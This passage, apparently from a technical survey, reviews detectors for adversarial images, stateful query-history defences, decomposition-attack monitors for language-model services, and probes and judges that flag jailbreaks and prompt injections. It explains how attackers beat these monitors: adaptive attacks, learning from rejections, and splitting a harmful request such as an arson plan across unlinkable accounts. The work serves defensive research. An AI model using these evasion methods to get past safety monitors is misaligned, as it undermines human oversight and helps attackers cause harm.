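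Later researchers tested their detectors against informed attackers, but often with attacks that were too weak. Ma and colleagues modified an attack to keep the estimated dimensionality low, and the modified attack failed on 96% to 100% of images, depending on the dataset and on how many layers the detector used. In *Obfuscated Gradients Give a False Sense of Security*, Athalye, Carlini and Wagner (2018) then cut the same defence's accuracy on CIFAR-10 to 5% without changing any pixel by more than about 3% of its range.

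Most attacks follow the gradient, which indicates how to change each pixel to bring the classifier closer to an error. Seven of the nine defences examined make the gradient useless as a guide, so the usual attacks fail, but an attacker who searches in another way can still find adversarial images. A failed attack may therefore mean only that the tester used the wrong attack.

Intrinsic dimensionality also failed against an attack that required no knowledge of the detector. *On the Limitation of Local Intrinsic Dimensionality for Characterizing the Subspaces* (Lu, Chen and Yu, 2018) found the score ineffective on adversarial images made on one network and used against another. An attacker who cannot see inside a commercial model can still make such images by training or downloading a substitute.

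Xu and colleagues tested feature squeezing on MNIST with an informed attack. When the attack could change pixels without limit, it succeeded on 68% of images, but many of the altered images looked visibly strange. When they capped the change to each pixel at 30% of its range, success fell to 1%. They did not run this test on colour images because they lacked a suitable version of one of the filters. *Bypassing Feature Squeezing by Increasing Adversary Strength* (2018) reports that stronger attacks readily bypassed the combined detector with minimal visible distortion.

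By 2020, testing defences with adaptive attacks was standard, and *On Adaptive Attacks to Adversarial Example Defenses* (Tramèr, Carlini and colleagues, 2020) examined how good those tests were. It covered thirteen recent defences, not all of them detectors, from three leading machine-learning conferences. The inventors had tried adaptive attacks themselves, yet Tramèr and colleagues circumvented all thirteen defences. No single strategy worked against every defence, and they argue that nobody can automate this kind of test because each attack must be carefully tailored to its target. A detector that survives a benchmark's fixed set of "adaptive" attacks has therefore passed a weaker test than it seems.

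### Why near-perfect detection is a surprising claim

Detecting altered images is closer in difficulty to classifying them correctly than many researchers assumed. They turned to detection because a detector only has to tell that something is wrong with an image, not work out what it really shows. But *Detecting Adversarial Examples Is (Nearly) As Hard As Classifying Them* (Tramèr, 2021) proves that a detector robust to changes of size *ε* can be turned into a classifier robust to changes of size *ε*/2.

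Here "detector" means a classifier that may also reject an input. It is robust on a clean image *x* if it labels *x* correctly and, for every image within distance *ε* of *x*, either gives the correct label or rejects. Rejecting *x* itself counts as a failure, since otherwise a detector could succeed by rejecting everything. The new classifier is not allowed to reject, and handles an input *z* as follows:

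1. Run the detector on *z*. If it gives a label, output that label.
2. If it rejects *z*, search all images within distance *ε*/2 of *z* for one that the detector accepts, and output the label of that image. If there is none, guess.

Suppose *ε* is 8 and an attacker has moved *x*, an image of a stop sign, by 4 to produce *z*. If the detector labels *z*, the label is correct, because *z* is within 8 of *x*. If it rejects *z*, the search covers every image within 4 of *z*. This includes *x*, which the detector accepts, so the search always finds an accepted image. That image may not be *x*, but it is at most 4 + 4 = 8 from *x*. The detector is robust up to that distance, so it labels the image "stop sign".

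Error-correcting codes work on the same principle. If a sender transmits 0 as 000 and 1 as 111, the receiver can detect up to two flipped digits, because it takes three flips to turn 000 into 111 or 111 into 000. The receiver can correct only one flip, by choosing whichever of 000 and 111 is closer to what it received.

Nobody can use this construction to turn a good detector into a usable classifier, because step 2 requires searching an astronomical number of nearby images. Tramèr describes this search as an intractable optimisation problem for a neural network. If unlimited computation at the time of use made robust classification much easier, detection could also be easier than robust classification in practice without contradicting the theorem.

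Tramèr argues that this is unlikely given what researchers know. The construction needs no training data beyond what the detector used, and the evidence suggests that a shortage of data limits robust classifiers more than a shortage of computation does. On CIFAR-10, for example, classifiers trained with the best methods are perfectly robust on the training images but not on new ones. He accepts that this is a reason for suspicion and not a proof.

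The result gives readers a way to check a published detection rate. The share of images a detector handles correctly under attack is at least

100% − false positive rate − share of attacks missed − ordinary error rate of the classifier.

One 2021 detector for CIFAR-10 had a false positive rate of 20%, missed 19% of attacks of size 4, and was paired with a classifier that had a 5% error rate. These rates imply that the detector and classifier together have at least 56% robust accuracy at size 4, which in turn implies that a classifier with at least 56% robust accuracy at size 2 exists. The best classifier Tramèr knew of had 10% robust accuracy at that size. Either the detector implied a huge, unreported advance in robust classification, or a stronger attack would beat it.

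Tramèr made the same comparison for 14 published detectors, and 12 of them, including all three described above, implied classifiers much better than the best available.

| Detector | Dataset | Implied robust accuracy at half the attack size | Best classifier at that size |
|---|---|---|---|
| Feature squeezing | ImageNet | At least 67% | 54% |
| Mahalanobis distance | CIFAR-10 | At least 81% | 59% |
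| Local intrinsic dimensionality | MNIST | At least 99% | 72% |

The middle column assumes that the published rates hold against every possible attack of the given size. Some inventors never claimed this, including Ma and colleagues, who offered their detector as a proof of concept and left robust detection to future work. A rate of 99% against a fixed list of attacks can be accurate without contradicting the theorem, and is implausible only if it is claimed for attackers in general.

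Results for defences with a mathematical guarantee closely match the theorem. On CIFAR-10, one classifier had a guaranteed accuracy of 39% for changes of up to 4/255 per pixel, and a separately developed detector had 37% for changes twice as large. Letting a system reject inputs seems to roughly double the size of change it can withstand, but do little more.

The proof also requires a measure of the attacker's changes whose distances can be added together. Standard measures of pixel change meet this requirement, but the usual measure for stickers and patches, the number of neighbouring pixels they cover, does not. The proof therefore does not cover the stickers on road signs, which Tramèr leaves as an open problem. The comparison figures are from 2022 or earlier, and a better classifier published since then would make the implied claims less surprising.

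### From classifiers to current models

Researchers still use these scores, though they have moved on from the classifiers they first tested them on. *Revisiting JBShield* (2026) calls Mahalanobis distance a standard way to detect adversarial examples from activations, and uses it to detect jailbreaks of language models. This does not show whether detection of altered images has improved, because a jailbreak prompt is text and need not be a small change to a harmless prompt.

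These methods are harder to apply to vision-language models, which take images and text and answer in words. Feature squeezing compares probabilities over a fixed list of classes, but a model asked to describe a photograph may word its answer differently after a slight blur even without an attack. The defender would have to compare meanings instead. Mahalanobis distance in Lee and colleagues' form needs a mean for each class, and an open-ended question has no classes. Intrinsic dimensionality would be the easiest to transfer because it needs only activations and a sample of ordinary inputs, but it had already failed on small classifiers.

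None of the experiments in the 2017 to 2022 papers involved a vision-language model, so their detection rates are not estimates for one. Tramèr's argument still applies where such a model makes a fixed choice, such as whether an uploaded image breaks a site's rules. A vendor who claims to detect nearly every small alteration that would flip that choice is, in effect, also claiming a robust classifier for it. The argument does not cover images that contain written instructions, because the attacker does not need to keep the change small.

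For a live service, a score on one image is most useful against people who reuse published attacks, with a threshold set on the service's own traffic. The score may also reveal an attacker who is still experimenting. Xu and colleagues' detector flagged 20% to 25% of attempts that failed to fool the classifier, several times its false positive rate. A stateful detector, which compares each query with earlier ones, could use such attempts as evidence.

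## Scoring the history of queries

An attacker who experiments on a live classifier leaves a series of similar images in the classifier's log. A stateful detector uses this series to flag the attack while the attacker is still searching for an adversarial input, even if no single image looks suspicious.

### Why attackers send similar queries

An attacker with a copy of the classifier can compute the gradient in private and use it to find an image that the classifier gets wrong. If the classifier is hosted, the attacker sees only its answers and has to estimate the gradient by sending slightly changed images and checking whether the answer changes. Even a colour image of 32 by 32 pixels has 3,072 values to adjust. Many services return only a label, which usually stays the same after a small change, so the attacker learns very little from each query.

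Published attacks do this in two ways. Some, such as NES, send many slightly different copies of an image and estimate the gradient from the answers. Others, such as the Boundary attack, start from an image that already gets the label the attacker wants and move it in small steps towards the image the attacker wants misread. Both often take thousands of queries. The queries look alike because the steps are small and the final image has to resemble the original. In *Blacklight*, Li, Shan and colleagues (2020) measured this on ImageNet and found that consecutive attack queries were on average 20 to 380 times closer together than random pairs of harmless images.

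### The distance to fifty neighbours

Chen, Carlini and Wagner (2019), in *Stateful Detection of Black-Box Adversarial Attacks*, proposed what they believed was the first detector to use this pattern against adversarial images. It keeps a separate history for each account and handles a query *x* in four steps:

1. A small neural network, the encoder *E*, turns the image into 256 numbers.
2. The software finds the 50 stored queries whose encodings are nearest and averages the distances: *d(x)* = (1/50) Σᵢ ‖*E(x)* − *E(xᵢ)*‖.
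3. If the average is below a threshold, the software flags the query.
4. After an alarm, it clears the account's history, and the service bans the account.

A small distance is the suspicious result here, so the score is the distance with its sign reversed.

The encoder is there because distances between raw pixels are easy to inflate. Adding 0.05 to every pixel value, on a scale from 0 to 1, moves a CIFAR-10 image by 2.77 units without changing what it shows. Chen and colleagues trained the encoder on pairs of images, with the loss

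‖*e* − *e⁺*‖² + max(0, *m*² − ‖*e′* − *e⁻*‖²).

The first term pulls together the encodings of an image and an altered copy of it, such as a rotated or brighter one. The second separates the encodings of two different images until they are at least *m* apart.

The threshold is set so that 0.1% of the CIFAR-10 training images would trigger an alarm if a user sent the whole set in random order. Averaging over more neighbours allows a larger threshold at the same false positive rate, which forces an attacker to spread queries further apart. This benefit levels off at around 50 neighbours. Using more neighbours also delays the first alarm, because the detector cannot compute a score until it has stored that many queries.

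A toy version with three neighbours shows how the steps fit together. Suppose the encoder produces a single number and the threshold is 0.5. An attacker sends variants of one image:

| Query | Encoding | Stored encodings | Distances to the three nearest | Average | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 2.0 | None | | | Store |
| 2 | 2.1 | 2.0 | | | Store |
| 3 | 2.3 | 2.0, 2.1 | | | Store |
| 4 | 2.2 | 2.0, 2.1, 2.3 | 0.2, 0.1, 0.1 | 0.13 | Alarm, clear history |
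| 5 | 2.4 | None | | | Store |

If an ordinary user's first three images have encodings of 2.0, 7.0 and 4.5 and the fourth has an encoding of 9.0, the average distance from the fourth to the other three is 4.5, and the detector raises no alarm. For the attacker, the history is empty again after query 4, so the next alarm can come at query 8 at the earliest. With three neighbours, the detector can therefore raise at most one alarm for every four queries.

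### Many alarms, and an attack that still succeeds

Chen and colleagues ran both kinds of attack against a CIFAR-10 classifier that returned only labels. Each attack had to make the classifier give a particular wrong label without changing any pixel by more than 5% of its range.

| Attack | Success rate | Average queries | Average alarms | Queries per alarm |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| NES | 100% | 325,200 | 6,377 | 51 |
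| Boundary | 100% | 14,720 | 288 | 51 |

With 50 neighbours, the design allows at most one alarm per 51 queries, and the detector reached that limit on both attacks. Both still succeeded every time, because an attacker whose account is banned can continue from a new one with everything learned so far. The defence therefore depends on how hard or expensive it is to open an account. Altering one image took 288 accounts, so the defence is strong if each account needs its own phone number or credit card, but weak if sign-up is free.

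Chen and colleagues also looked for ways to hide the attack. The best method disguised each query so that the stored images looked unrelated but the answers were still informative. It succeeded 76% of the time and set off 97 alarms over 13,400 queries, about one per 138. With raw pixel distances instead of the encoder, the same attack would have set off only 12 alarms. This result depends on keeping the encoder secret, and an attacker can learn a little about it by watching which accounts get banned.

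One study estimated the time and money an attacker would need to avoid every alarm from a single account, assuming the attacker somehow knew exactly when the next one was due. If the service kept each query for 100 hours, waiting out 97 alarms would take over a year. If it kept the last 10,000 queries instead, the attacker could push out the old ones with random images, which would cost about $1,500 per adversarial image at 2019 prices. Without the detector, the study's best attack cost about $20.

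The false positive rate of 0.1% per query is harder to interpret. At that rate, a customer who sends 1,000 harmless images has a 63% chance of at least one alarm, and an alarm means a ban. The rate would be lower for an account with a short history, because the nearest stored images are usually further from a new query, and higher for a customer who sends video frames or several shots of the same scene. Chen and colleagues measured the rate on a dataset of unrelated pictures and acknowledged that a real service might need a lower one.

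### Blacklight: one store for all accounts

Li and colleagues assumed that attackers can get as many accounts as they like. Blacklight, their detector, therefore compares each query with those from every account and rejects suspicious queries instead of banning anyone. Searching everyone's queries requires a much faster comparison, which it gets from fingerprints made of hashes:

1. Round the pixel values to coarse steps, which removes many tiny changes.
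2. Write the pixels out as one long row and hash every run of 20 consecutive values, together with a secret number. A CIFAR-10 image gives 3,053 hashes.
3. Keep the 50 highest hashes as the fingerprint.
4. Reject the query if it shares more than 25 hashes with any stored fingerprint.

Changing one pixel value affects at most 20 of the 3,053 hashes, so the fingerprint usually stays the same or nearly so. An attacker without the secret number cannot work out which parts of the image ended up in the fingerprint.

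Li and colleagues derived a limit on how often two images will match. If *D* of the *N* hashes differ between them, and a fingerprint keeps *S* hashes, the probability of sharing more than *T* is at most

Σₖ C(*N* − *D*, *k*) · C(*D*, *S* − *k*) / C(*N*, *S*), summed from *k* = *T* + 1 up to *S*,

where C(*a*, *b*) is the number of ways to choose *b* items from *a*. This is the chance of drawing more than *T* shared hashes in *S* random draws. For CIFAR-10 it is above 99% when 30% of the hashes differ, about 44% when half differ, and below 0.1% when 70% differ. Measured match rates followed the formula closely. The detector therefore works well as long as attack queries stay in the first range and harmless images in the last.

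In tests on four image datasets, it detected every attack. On CIFAR-10, the first rejection came after 2 to 6 queries for four of the five attacks and after 28 for the Boundary attack. No attack succeeded within 100,000 queries, and the false positive rate was below 0.1%. The fingerprints of a million queries take up about 2 gigabytes. Even if a service deletes them every day, an attacker who stopped at each rejection and waited for the next deletion would need about three years to complete an attack.

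Li and colleagues also ran the 2019 detector on CIFAR-10. It flagged 1.0% to 1.8% of attack queries, while Blacklight flagged 68.8% to 99.6%. Most of this gap comes from what the two systems do after an alarm, rather than from how well they recognise attacks. The 2019 detector clears its history after each alarm and then needs 50 stored queries before it can raise another, so it cannot flag more than 2% of queries. The difference still matters, because persistent attackers succeeded 78% to 100% of the time against the 2019 detector.

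When many people upload the same popular picture to a service with a shared store, Blacklight as described would reject all but the first upload, because identical images have identical fingerprints. The test datasets contain few duplicates, so the measured false positive rate may be too low for a service where duplicates are common.

### What a rejection tells the attacker

Feng, Fawaz and colleagues re-tested four stateful detectors, including the two above, in *Stateful Defenses for Machine Learning Models Are Not Yet Secure* (2023). Ordinary attacks never succeeded against Blacklight on any of three image datasets. When the attacks adapted to the detector's responses, at least one succeeded 99% of the time or more on every dataset. The same was true for PIHA, a similar detector with a different fingerprint. The adapted Boundary attack, however, succeeded only 38% of the time against Blacklight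 on ImageNet.

The weakness is that attackers can learn from each rejection or acceptance whether their last query was too close to an earlier one. With enough of these responses, they can keep later queries just far enough from earlier ones to avoid rejection. Blacklight still slowed the attack, but not by much. NES on CIFAR-10 needed about 1,500 queries instead of 900, and Feng and colleagues estimated that the extra queries would cost $1 to $18 on commercial services.

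The 2019 detector failed to stop attacks even without any such adaptation. Feng and colleagues completed each of six attacks with between 2 and 21 accounts, far fewer than the hundreds or thousands in the original tests. The attacks needed fewer accounts because they needed fewer queries. The detector still recognised attacks as well as before, and most used up about one account per 50 queries. NES took 861 queries on average when the service returned confidence values, compared with 325,200 in the original test, where the service returned only labels.

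Operators can try to reveal less to attackers. Chen and colleagues suggested delaying bans until preset points, so that the attacker cannot tell which query set off the alarm. Li and colleagues considered sending false answers to suspected attackers but decided against it, partly because these take much more work to produce than rejections. A harmless customer who set off the alarm would also get a wrong answer without knowing it.

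### The trade-off with false alarms

A stricter threshold does not solve the problem. When Feng and colleagues made Blacklight flag images that were less alike, its false positive rate on about a million images rose from 0.2% to 0.9%, but every attack they tried still succeeded more than 63% of the time. The attacks adapted by spacing their queries further apart.

*Theoretically Principled Trade-off for Stateful Defenses* (Hooda, Mangaokar and colleagues, 2023) derives upper limits on the detection rate for a general class of encoders and shows how the trade-off between detection and false alarms affects an attack's progress. A detector based on similarity can separate attacks from normal use only if attack queries are closer together than harmless ones. If an attacker can make progress with queries as far apart as two ordinary photographs of the same street, a threshold that catches the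 attack will also flag the photographs.

*Query Provenance Analysis* (Li, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) scores the relationships among a whole sequence of queries rather than only the closest match, because an attack's queries build on one another in a way that ordinary traffic does not. Its inventors report that it cut the success rate of the 2023 attacks to about 4%, compared with 78% against Blacklight and 88% against PIHA. Like Blacklight's original results, these figures come from the inventors' own tests.

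### Attacks that need no queries

A score based on query history cannot detect an attacker who prepares an adversarial image on a substitute classifier and sends only the finished version, because the log then contains just one query from the attacker and no earlier ones to compare it to.

Chen and colleagues tested such attacks on CIFAR-10. Images made on a substitute model fooled an unprotected classifier 59% to 74% of the time when any wrong label counted as success, and 19% of the time when the attacker needed a particular one. They suggested combining the detector with a classifier trained on adversarial images from several other models. This cut the rates to between 14% and 16% for any wrong label and 1% for a particular one, but nearly doubled the classifier's error rate on ordinary images, from 7.8% to 14.6%.

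Attackers who will accept any misclassified image do not need a substitute. They can send random photographs to a classifier with 92% accuracy and expect an error after about 13 queries.

### Harmful requests in harmless pieces

Language-model services face a different kind of repeated query, the decomposition attack, in which an attacker splits a forbidden request into questions that are each acceptable and combines the answers. *TwinGate* (Sun, Li and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of someone planning to burn down a house for the insurance money, who asks separately about overloaded circuits, old wiring and the way cables heat up. An electrician might ask any of these questions. A monitor can read them together when they all arrive in one conversation or agent session, but an attacker avoids this by spreading them over several accounts.

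The image detectors would miss such an attack because its queries are not alike. TwinGate, published in April 2026, therefore trains an encoder to place questions with the same harmful purpose close together, even when they share no words or topic. For each harmful query *i* in a training batch, the loss is

*Lᵢ* = −(1/|*P*|) Σₚ ln [ exp(*zᵢ* · *zₚ* / *τ*) / Σⱼ exp(*zᵢ* · *zⱼ* / *τ*) ],

where *z* is a query's encoding, *P* is the set of other queries in the batch with the same harmful purpose, *p* runs over *P*, *j* runs over every other query in the batch, and *τ* controls how sharply the loss reacts to differences in similarity. Suppose a batch holds one partner for query *i*, with a similarity of 0.2, and one harmless query, with a similarity of 0.6. If *τ* is 0.1, the loss is about 4. If training moves the similarities to 0.8 and 0.1, the loss drops to about 0.001. Harmless queries only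 push harmful ones away and never attract each other. When the developers let them attract each other too, performance collapsed.

TwinGate also uses a second encoder, which captures literal meaning and which they left untrained. At run time the system ignores accounts and keeps one store of past queries:

1. If the new query means almost the same as a stored one, copy the earlier decision.
2. Otherwise, if its purpose encoding is close enough to that of any stored query, block it.
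3. Otherwise, allow it. In every case, store both encodings and the decision.

The first step stops a harmless question from looking like a coordinated attack just because many people ask it. It also means that a question TwinGate wrongly blocks once stays blocked for later users. The developers tried to exploit this by planting misleading queries, but the false positive rate did not rise.

In tests on harmful purposes it had not seen in training, TwinGate blocked at least one piece of more than 76% of the attacks, with a false positive rate below 0.2%. On a subset of the test data, the first block came at the third piece on average, so the attacker usually got one or two answers. In live tests, an automated attacker succeeded 99% of the time without TwinGate and 9% with it. Rewording every piece raised the success rate against TwinGate to 16%, and an attack that used TwinGate's own parameters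 reached 18%.

TwinGate handles more than 1,700 requests per second on four processors. At that speed, a false positive rate of 0.2% means about three wrongly blocked requests every second. One processor's memory holds the encodings of about 6 million requests, roughly an hour of traffic at full speed. Merging similar entries let TwinGate work almost as well with space for only a quarter of the requests, and larger databases would cover a longer period. If an attacker can wait for days, the store may still lose their earlier requests.

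### When nobody can link the accounts

TwinGate's test left out a difficult group of harmless users, those who ask for exactly the same things as the attacker. *Decomposition Attacks Across Unlinkable Identities* (Sun, Zhao and colleagues, August 2026), which shares two authors with TwinGate, presents a test built around these users. The test contains 91 computer-security programming tasks that commercial models refuse when asked outright. The attacker splits these into 365 smaller pieces of code, each of which a model will write. The test also includes 11,393 harmless requests for the same pieces, checked by running the code that models wrote in reply, and a large body of unrelated traffic.

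The attacker can send every request from a new account that the service cannot link to the others. The study allowed each defence to block at most 1% of the harmless requests for the same pieces and 0.5% of unrelated ones. It set the thresholds on separate data, then tested eight defences on 20 groups of related tasks and on 11 further groups not used to build the defences. The table shows the results when the attacker made only one attempt at each piece. "Same" is the share of harmless requests for the same pieces that the defence blocked, and "Unrelated" is the share of other harmless requests that it blocked.

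| Defence | Attack success, 20 groups | Same | Unrelated | Attack success, 11 new groups | Same | Unrelated |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Word-pattern classifier, one request at a time | 94.6% | 1.3% | 0% | 100% | 0% | 0% |
| Granite Guardian, one request at a time | 100% | 0% | 0.5% | 99.0% | 0.3% | 0.5% |
| TwinGate | 100% | 0% | 0% | 100% | 0% | 0% |
| Clusters of similar requests, read by a judge model | 100% | 0% | 0% | 100% | 0% | 0% |
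| Running summary, read by a judge model | 97.6% | 0.6% | 0.1% | 2.5% | 64.7% | 0.1% |
| Earlier requests and task descriptions, read by a judge model | 94.4% | 1.4% | 0% | 48.6% | 19.0% | 0% |
| Record of capabilities given out, read by a judge model | 100% | 0% | 0% | 100% | 0% | 0% |
| Matching to the 365 known pieces | 93.9% | 1.4% | 0% | 83.5% | 4.6% | 0% |

No defence that stayed within both limits reduced attack success below 97%. The two largest reductions, to 2.5% and 48.6%, came from blocking 64.7% and 19.0% of the harmless requests for the same pieces. TwinGate blocked nothing at the threshold chosen for it. With looser settings that still met the 1% limit, it blocked 43% to 63% of unrelated traffic. The study did not retrain TwinGate for these tasks, so its results partly reflect how well it transfers to a new subject.

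The defences failed because they could not distinguish an attacker's request from a harmless request for the same piece. The difference lies in who collects the answers, and the collecting happens outside the service. The defences could identify what was being requested, since five of the eight scores separated requests for the 365 pieces from unrelated traffic with an AUROC of at least 0.969.

Sun, Zhao and colleagues prove how much protection is possible in this situation, even for a defender that knows exactly what each request provides. Suppose an attack needs three pieces, and harmless users send 10, 20 and 30 requests for them. The cheapest way to stop the attack is to refuse everyone the first piece, which blocks 10 harmless requests. Doing this half the time blocks 5 on average and stops half the attacks. If the attacker makes one attempt and looks like everyone else, the lowest possible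 success rate is

max(0, 1 − *B*/*D*),

where *B* is the average number of harmless requests blocked and *D* is the number the defender must block to stop every attack. In their data, *D* was 17.5% of the harmless requests for the same pieces. That share may be a tiny part of all traffic. If 1% of a service's harmless requests were of this kind, it would come to less than 0.2% of the total, though the cost would fall entirely on people doing legitimate security work.

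Accounts can help when harmless users behave differently from attackers. If harmless users keep the same accounts and attackers always use new ones, an ideal defender can stop every attack that makes one attempt per piece, while blocking about 0.8% of the harmless requests for the same pieces. But this advantage disappears once attackers can retry. By the study's calculation, attacks would succeed 37% of the time with two attempts per piece and 92% with sixteen. In a separate experiment, attackers who saw only whether the service allowed or blocked each request learned which kinds of request got through, and succeeded 99.4% of the time, compared with 47.2% for a fixed strategy. As with Blacklight, each refusal helped the attacker, while the defender never learned whether the blocked request was part of an attack.

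The mathematical result is better supported than the exact percentages in the table. The tasks are synthetic, and no public data show how often real users ask for the same things as attackers. When these shared requests were rarer, some defences did better, with attack success as low as 40% on the first attempt and 84% by the fifth. The harmless requests also began with a shared 162-character introduction, and four of the judge models read only the first 400 characters, so they rarely reached the request itself. Because of how the study assigned roles, this introduction didn't reveal which requests were attacks, but it may have made those judges look worse than they are.

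To do better, a service needs information that the requests do not contain, or a way to make it harder to create new identities and retry. The study suggests reliable account linking, payment, rate limits and restrictions on what users can do with the answers. Identity checks would restore the difficulty of getting new accounts, which made the 2019 detector useful, but they would also exclude some legitimate users and reduce privacy for the rest.

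## Scoring prompts to language models

An attacker who needs only one prompt leaves no history for a stateful detector to compare, so services also score each prompt on its own for signs of a jailbreak or prompt injection. The score can come from a separate text classifier, a second language model acting as a judge, or a probe on the activations of the model that answers.

### Three kinds of detector

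A text classifier is usually a small language model fine-tuned on prompts labelled malicious or harmless. It outputs the probability that a prompt is malicious, so the operator can set a threshold. It needs only the text, so even a customer of a hosted model can run it.

A judge is a general-purpose language model with written instructions to decide whether a prompt is malicious. The operator can change the policy by editing the instructions, without collecting new training data. The main drawback is cost. Kramár, Engels and colleagues (2026) point out in *Building Production-Ready Probes For Gemini* that a judge as capable as the monitored model could double the cost of each request. A judge also normally answers yes or no, so the operator has no threshold to adjust.

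A probe uses activations that the monitored model already computes, so the only extra computation is the probe's own arithmetic. In tests at Google DeepMind, Kramár and colleagues' probes cost over 10,000 times less to run than language-model judges. But only an organisation that runs the model itself has access to its activations.

Fomin compared the three kinds of detector on his collection of 105,000 prompts. The text classifiers were Prompt Guard 2 and LlamaGuard, both from Meta. The judge was Llama 3.1 8B, and the probe used the same model's activations. He tested the probe on each dataset after training it on all the others. The table gives the percentage of each type of attack that each detector caught, with the probe at two thresholds.

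| Prompts | Prompt Guard 2 | LlamaGuard | Judge | Probe, threshold 0.5 | Probe, threshold 0.9 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Direct harmful requests | 36.7 | 97.4 | 85.8 | 69.7 | 64.7 |
| Jailbreaks | 48.5 | 28.9 | 60.0 | 71.2 | 59.5 |
| Indirect injections (in emails and similar text) | 37.3 | 27.4 | 7.1 | 66.7 | 53.1 |
| Injections in an agent's tool results | Not applicable | Not applicable | 21.5 | 99.2 | 91.5 |
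| Attempts to extract hidden information | 100.0 | 15.2 | 31.8 | 79.2 | 68.7 |
| Harmless prompts wrongly flagged | 0.4 | 3.0 | 4.4 | 6.8 | 3.7 |

No detector is best on every type of input. LlamaGuard catches nearly all direct harmful requests, which Meta trained it to recognise, but only about a quarter of indirect injections. The probe catches many more of the injections but misses about a third of the direct requests. Fomin could not test either of Meta's classifiers on tool results because neither accepts descriptions of an agent's tools.

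The judge's 7.1% result on indirect injections depends heavily on its instructions. Fomin tried four versions of the instructions on about 10,000 indirect injections and harmless prompts. Detection ranged from 11%, with a false positive rate of 1.4%, to 93%, with a false positive rate of 18.9%. With instructions to act as a security analyst, the model caught 93% of injections but also flagged 91% of the harmless emails in one dataset and 41% of the ordinary questions in another, so a company could hardly use this version on live traffic. The best usable version caught 46% of injections at a false positive rate of 3.5%, compared with 68% for the probe at the same rate.

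This judge was small, so the result does not mean that probes beat judges in general. In Kramár and colleagues' tests, Gemini 2.5 Flash, a much more capable 2025 model, performed slightly better as a judge than their chosen probe did.

### From token scores to one number

Kramár and colleagues built their probes to detect requests for help with cyberattacks. The simplest is a linear probe. A prompt *S* has *n* tokens, and *xⱼ* is the list of activations at token *j* in one middle layer of the model. The probe has a learned list of weights *w*, one per activation, and its score is

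*f(S)* = (1/*n*) Σⱼ *w* · *xⱼ*,

where the dot means multiplying matching entries and adding up the results. A further learned number *b* and the function σ(*z*) = 1/(1 + *e*⁻ᶻ) turn the score into a probability, σ(*f(S)* + *b*). The service flags the prompt if this exceeds a threshold.

Suppose each token has two activations, the weights are 2 and −1, and *b* is −1. A token with activations 1.5 and 0.5 scores 2.5, and one with activations 0.5 and 1 scores 0. The average for a prompt of these two tokens is 1.25, and adding *b* gives a probability of σ(0.25), or 0.56. Training adjusts *w* and *b* to lower the loss on labelled prompts.

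Averaging token scores works poorly on long prompts, because a short malicious request contributes very little to the average over a large body of harmless code. Taking the highest token score avoids this problem, but a longer text gives more chances for a harmless token to score high by accident. A moving average is a compromise between the two. One version, which Anthropic researchers proposed in 2025, gives half the weight to the current token and half to the running average, then takes the highest value reached. Another averages the scores in every run of ten tokens and takes the highest average.

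The invented example below compares these methods on two 1,000-token prompts. Ordinary tokens score −1, and any total above 0 raises an alarm.

| Prompt | Average of all tokens | Highest token | Highest running average | Highest ten-token average |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ten neighbouring malicious tokens, each scoring 5 | −0.94 | 5 | 4.99 | 5 |
| Harmless, with one stray token scoring 4 | −0.995 | 4 | 1.5 | −0.5 |

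Only the ten-token average classifies both prompts correctly. The average of all tokens misses the attack, and the other two methods flag the harmless prompt.

Kramár and colleagues also used attention probes, which learn how much weight each token should get in the average. For one set of learned weights, the score is

Σⱼ exp(*q* · *yⱼ*)(*v* · *yⱼ*) / Σⱼ exp(*q* · *yⱼ*),

where *yⱼ* is a processed version of the activations at token *j*, *v* produces the token's score and *q* determines its importance. The probe they selected for further tests computes this kind of weighted average within each ten-token window and keeps the highest result.

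The next table shows why the method matters. The long harmless prompts averaged more than 900,000 tokens, mostly code. The long attacks contain a harmful request placed before, after or among similar code. The "story" attacks are harmful requests that Gemini 2.5 Pro rewrote as narratives.

| Detector | Harmless coding prompts flagged | Long harmless prompts flagged | Harmless security questions flagged | Short attacks caught | Long attacks caught | Story attacks caught |
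|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Linear probe, average | 1.1% | 0.5% | 11.4% | 86.3% | 0.9% | 52.4% |
| Linear probe, running average | 1.0% | 13.6% | 16.8% | 88.6% | 98.3% | 85.9% |
| Attention probe | 0.3% | 0.0% | 10.1% | 90.0% | 12.1% | 56.6% |
| Selected probe | 0.7% | 1.2% | 6.7% | 91.4% | 97.0% | 57.5% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash as judge | 0.3% | 0.7% | 14.1% | 91.4% | 93.9% | 79.4% |

The plain average caught fewer than 1% of long attacks. The running average caught nearly all of them but flagged one in seven long harmless prompts. The selected probe avoided both failures, although it was trained only on short prompts. Training an attention probe on long prompts also worked, but took 22 times the resources.

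These figures depend on how the researchers chose the thresholds. They counted a false alarm on an ordinary prompt as ten times worse than a missed attack, and a missed attack as two and a half times worse than a false alarm on a harmless security question. A service for security professionals might weigh those errors differently.

### Passing doubtful prompts to a costlier check

A false positive rate of 0.7% is too high for a probe to block prompts by itself. If 10 of a million requests are attacks, the selected probe would catch about nine of them and flag 7,000 harmless requests. Operators can reduce this problem with a cascade, in which a cheap detector handles the clear cases and an expensive one handles the rest. Kramár and colleagues' version has two thresholds:

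1. If the probe's score is at or below the lower threshold, allow the prompt.
2. If it is at or above the upper threshold, flag the prompt.
3. If it is in between, send the prompt to a judge and use the judge's verdict.

The cascade runs the probe on every prompt and the judge on only some, so its average cost per prompt is the probe's cost plus the judge's cost multiplied by the share of prompts the judge receives. With Gemini 2.5 Flash as the judge, the cascade made fewer weighted errors than Flash alone at about one-fiftieth of the cost. Sending 8% of prompts to Flash also gave a lower error than using the probe or Flash alone. The cost saving is much better established than the gain in accuracy, because the error bars for most of these settings overlap.

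A simpler design sends everything the probe flags to the judge. In the example above, the judge would receive about 7,000 harmless requests. If it wrongly flagged 0.3% of them, the rate measured on ordinary coding prompts, about 21 false alarms would remain. But the requests that trigger the probe are probably harder to classify than average. If they were as hard as the harmless security questions, of which Flash flagged 14%, nearly 1,000 false alarms would remain. Testing the two detectors separately therefore doesn't show how well they work together.

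Google has put probes that detect cyberattack requests into the public versions of Gemini, and Kramár and colleagues report that their findings informed this deployment. The error rates above come from test sets, not live traffic. Some of the harmless test prompts came from real users, with personal details removed, which makes them a better guide than invented ones.

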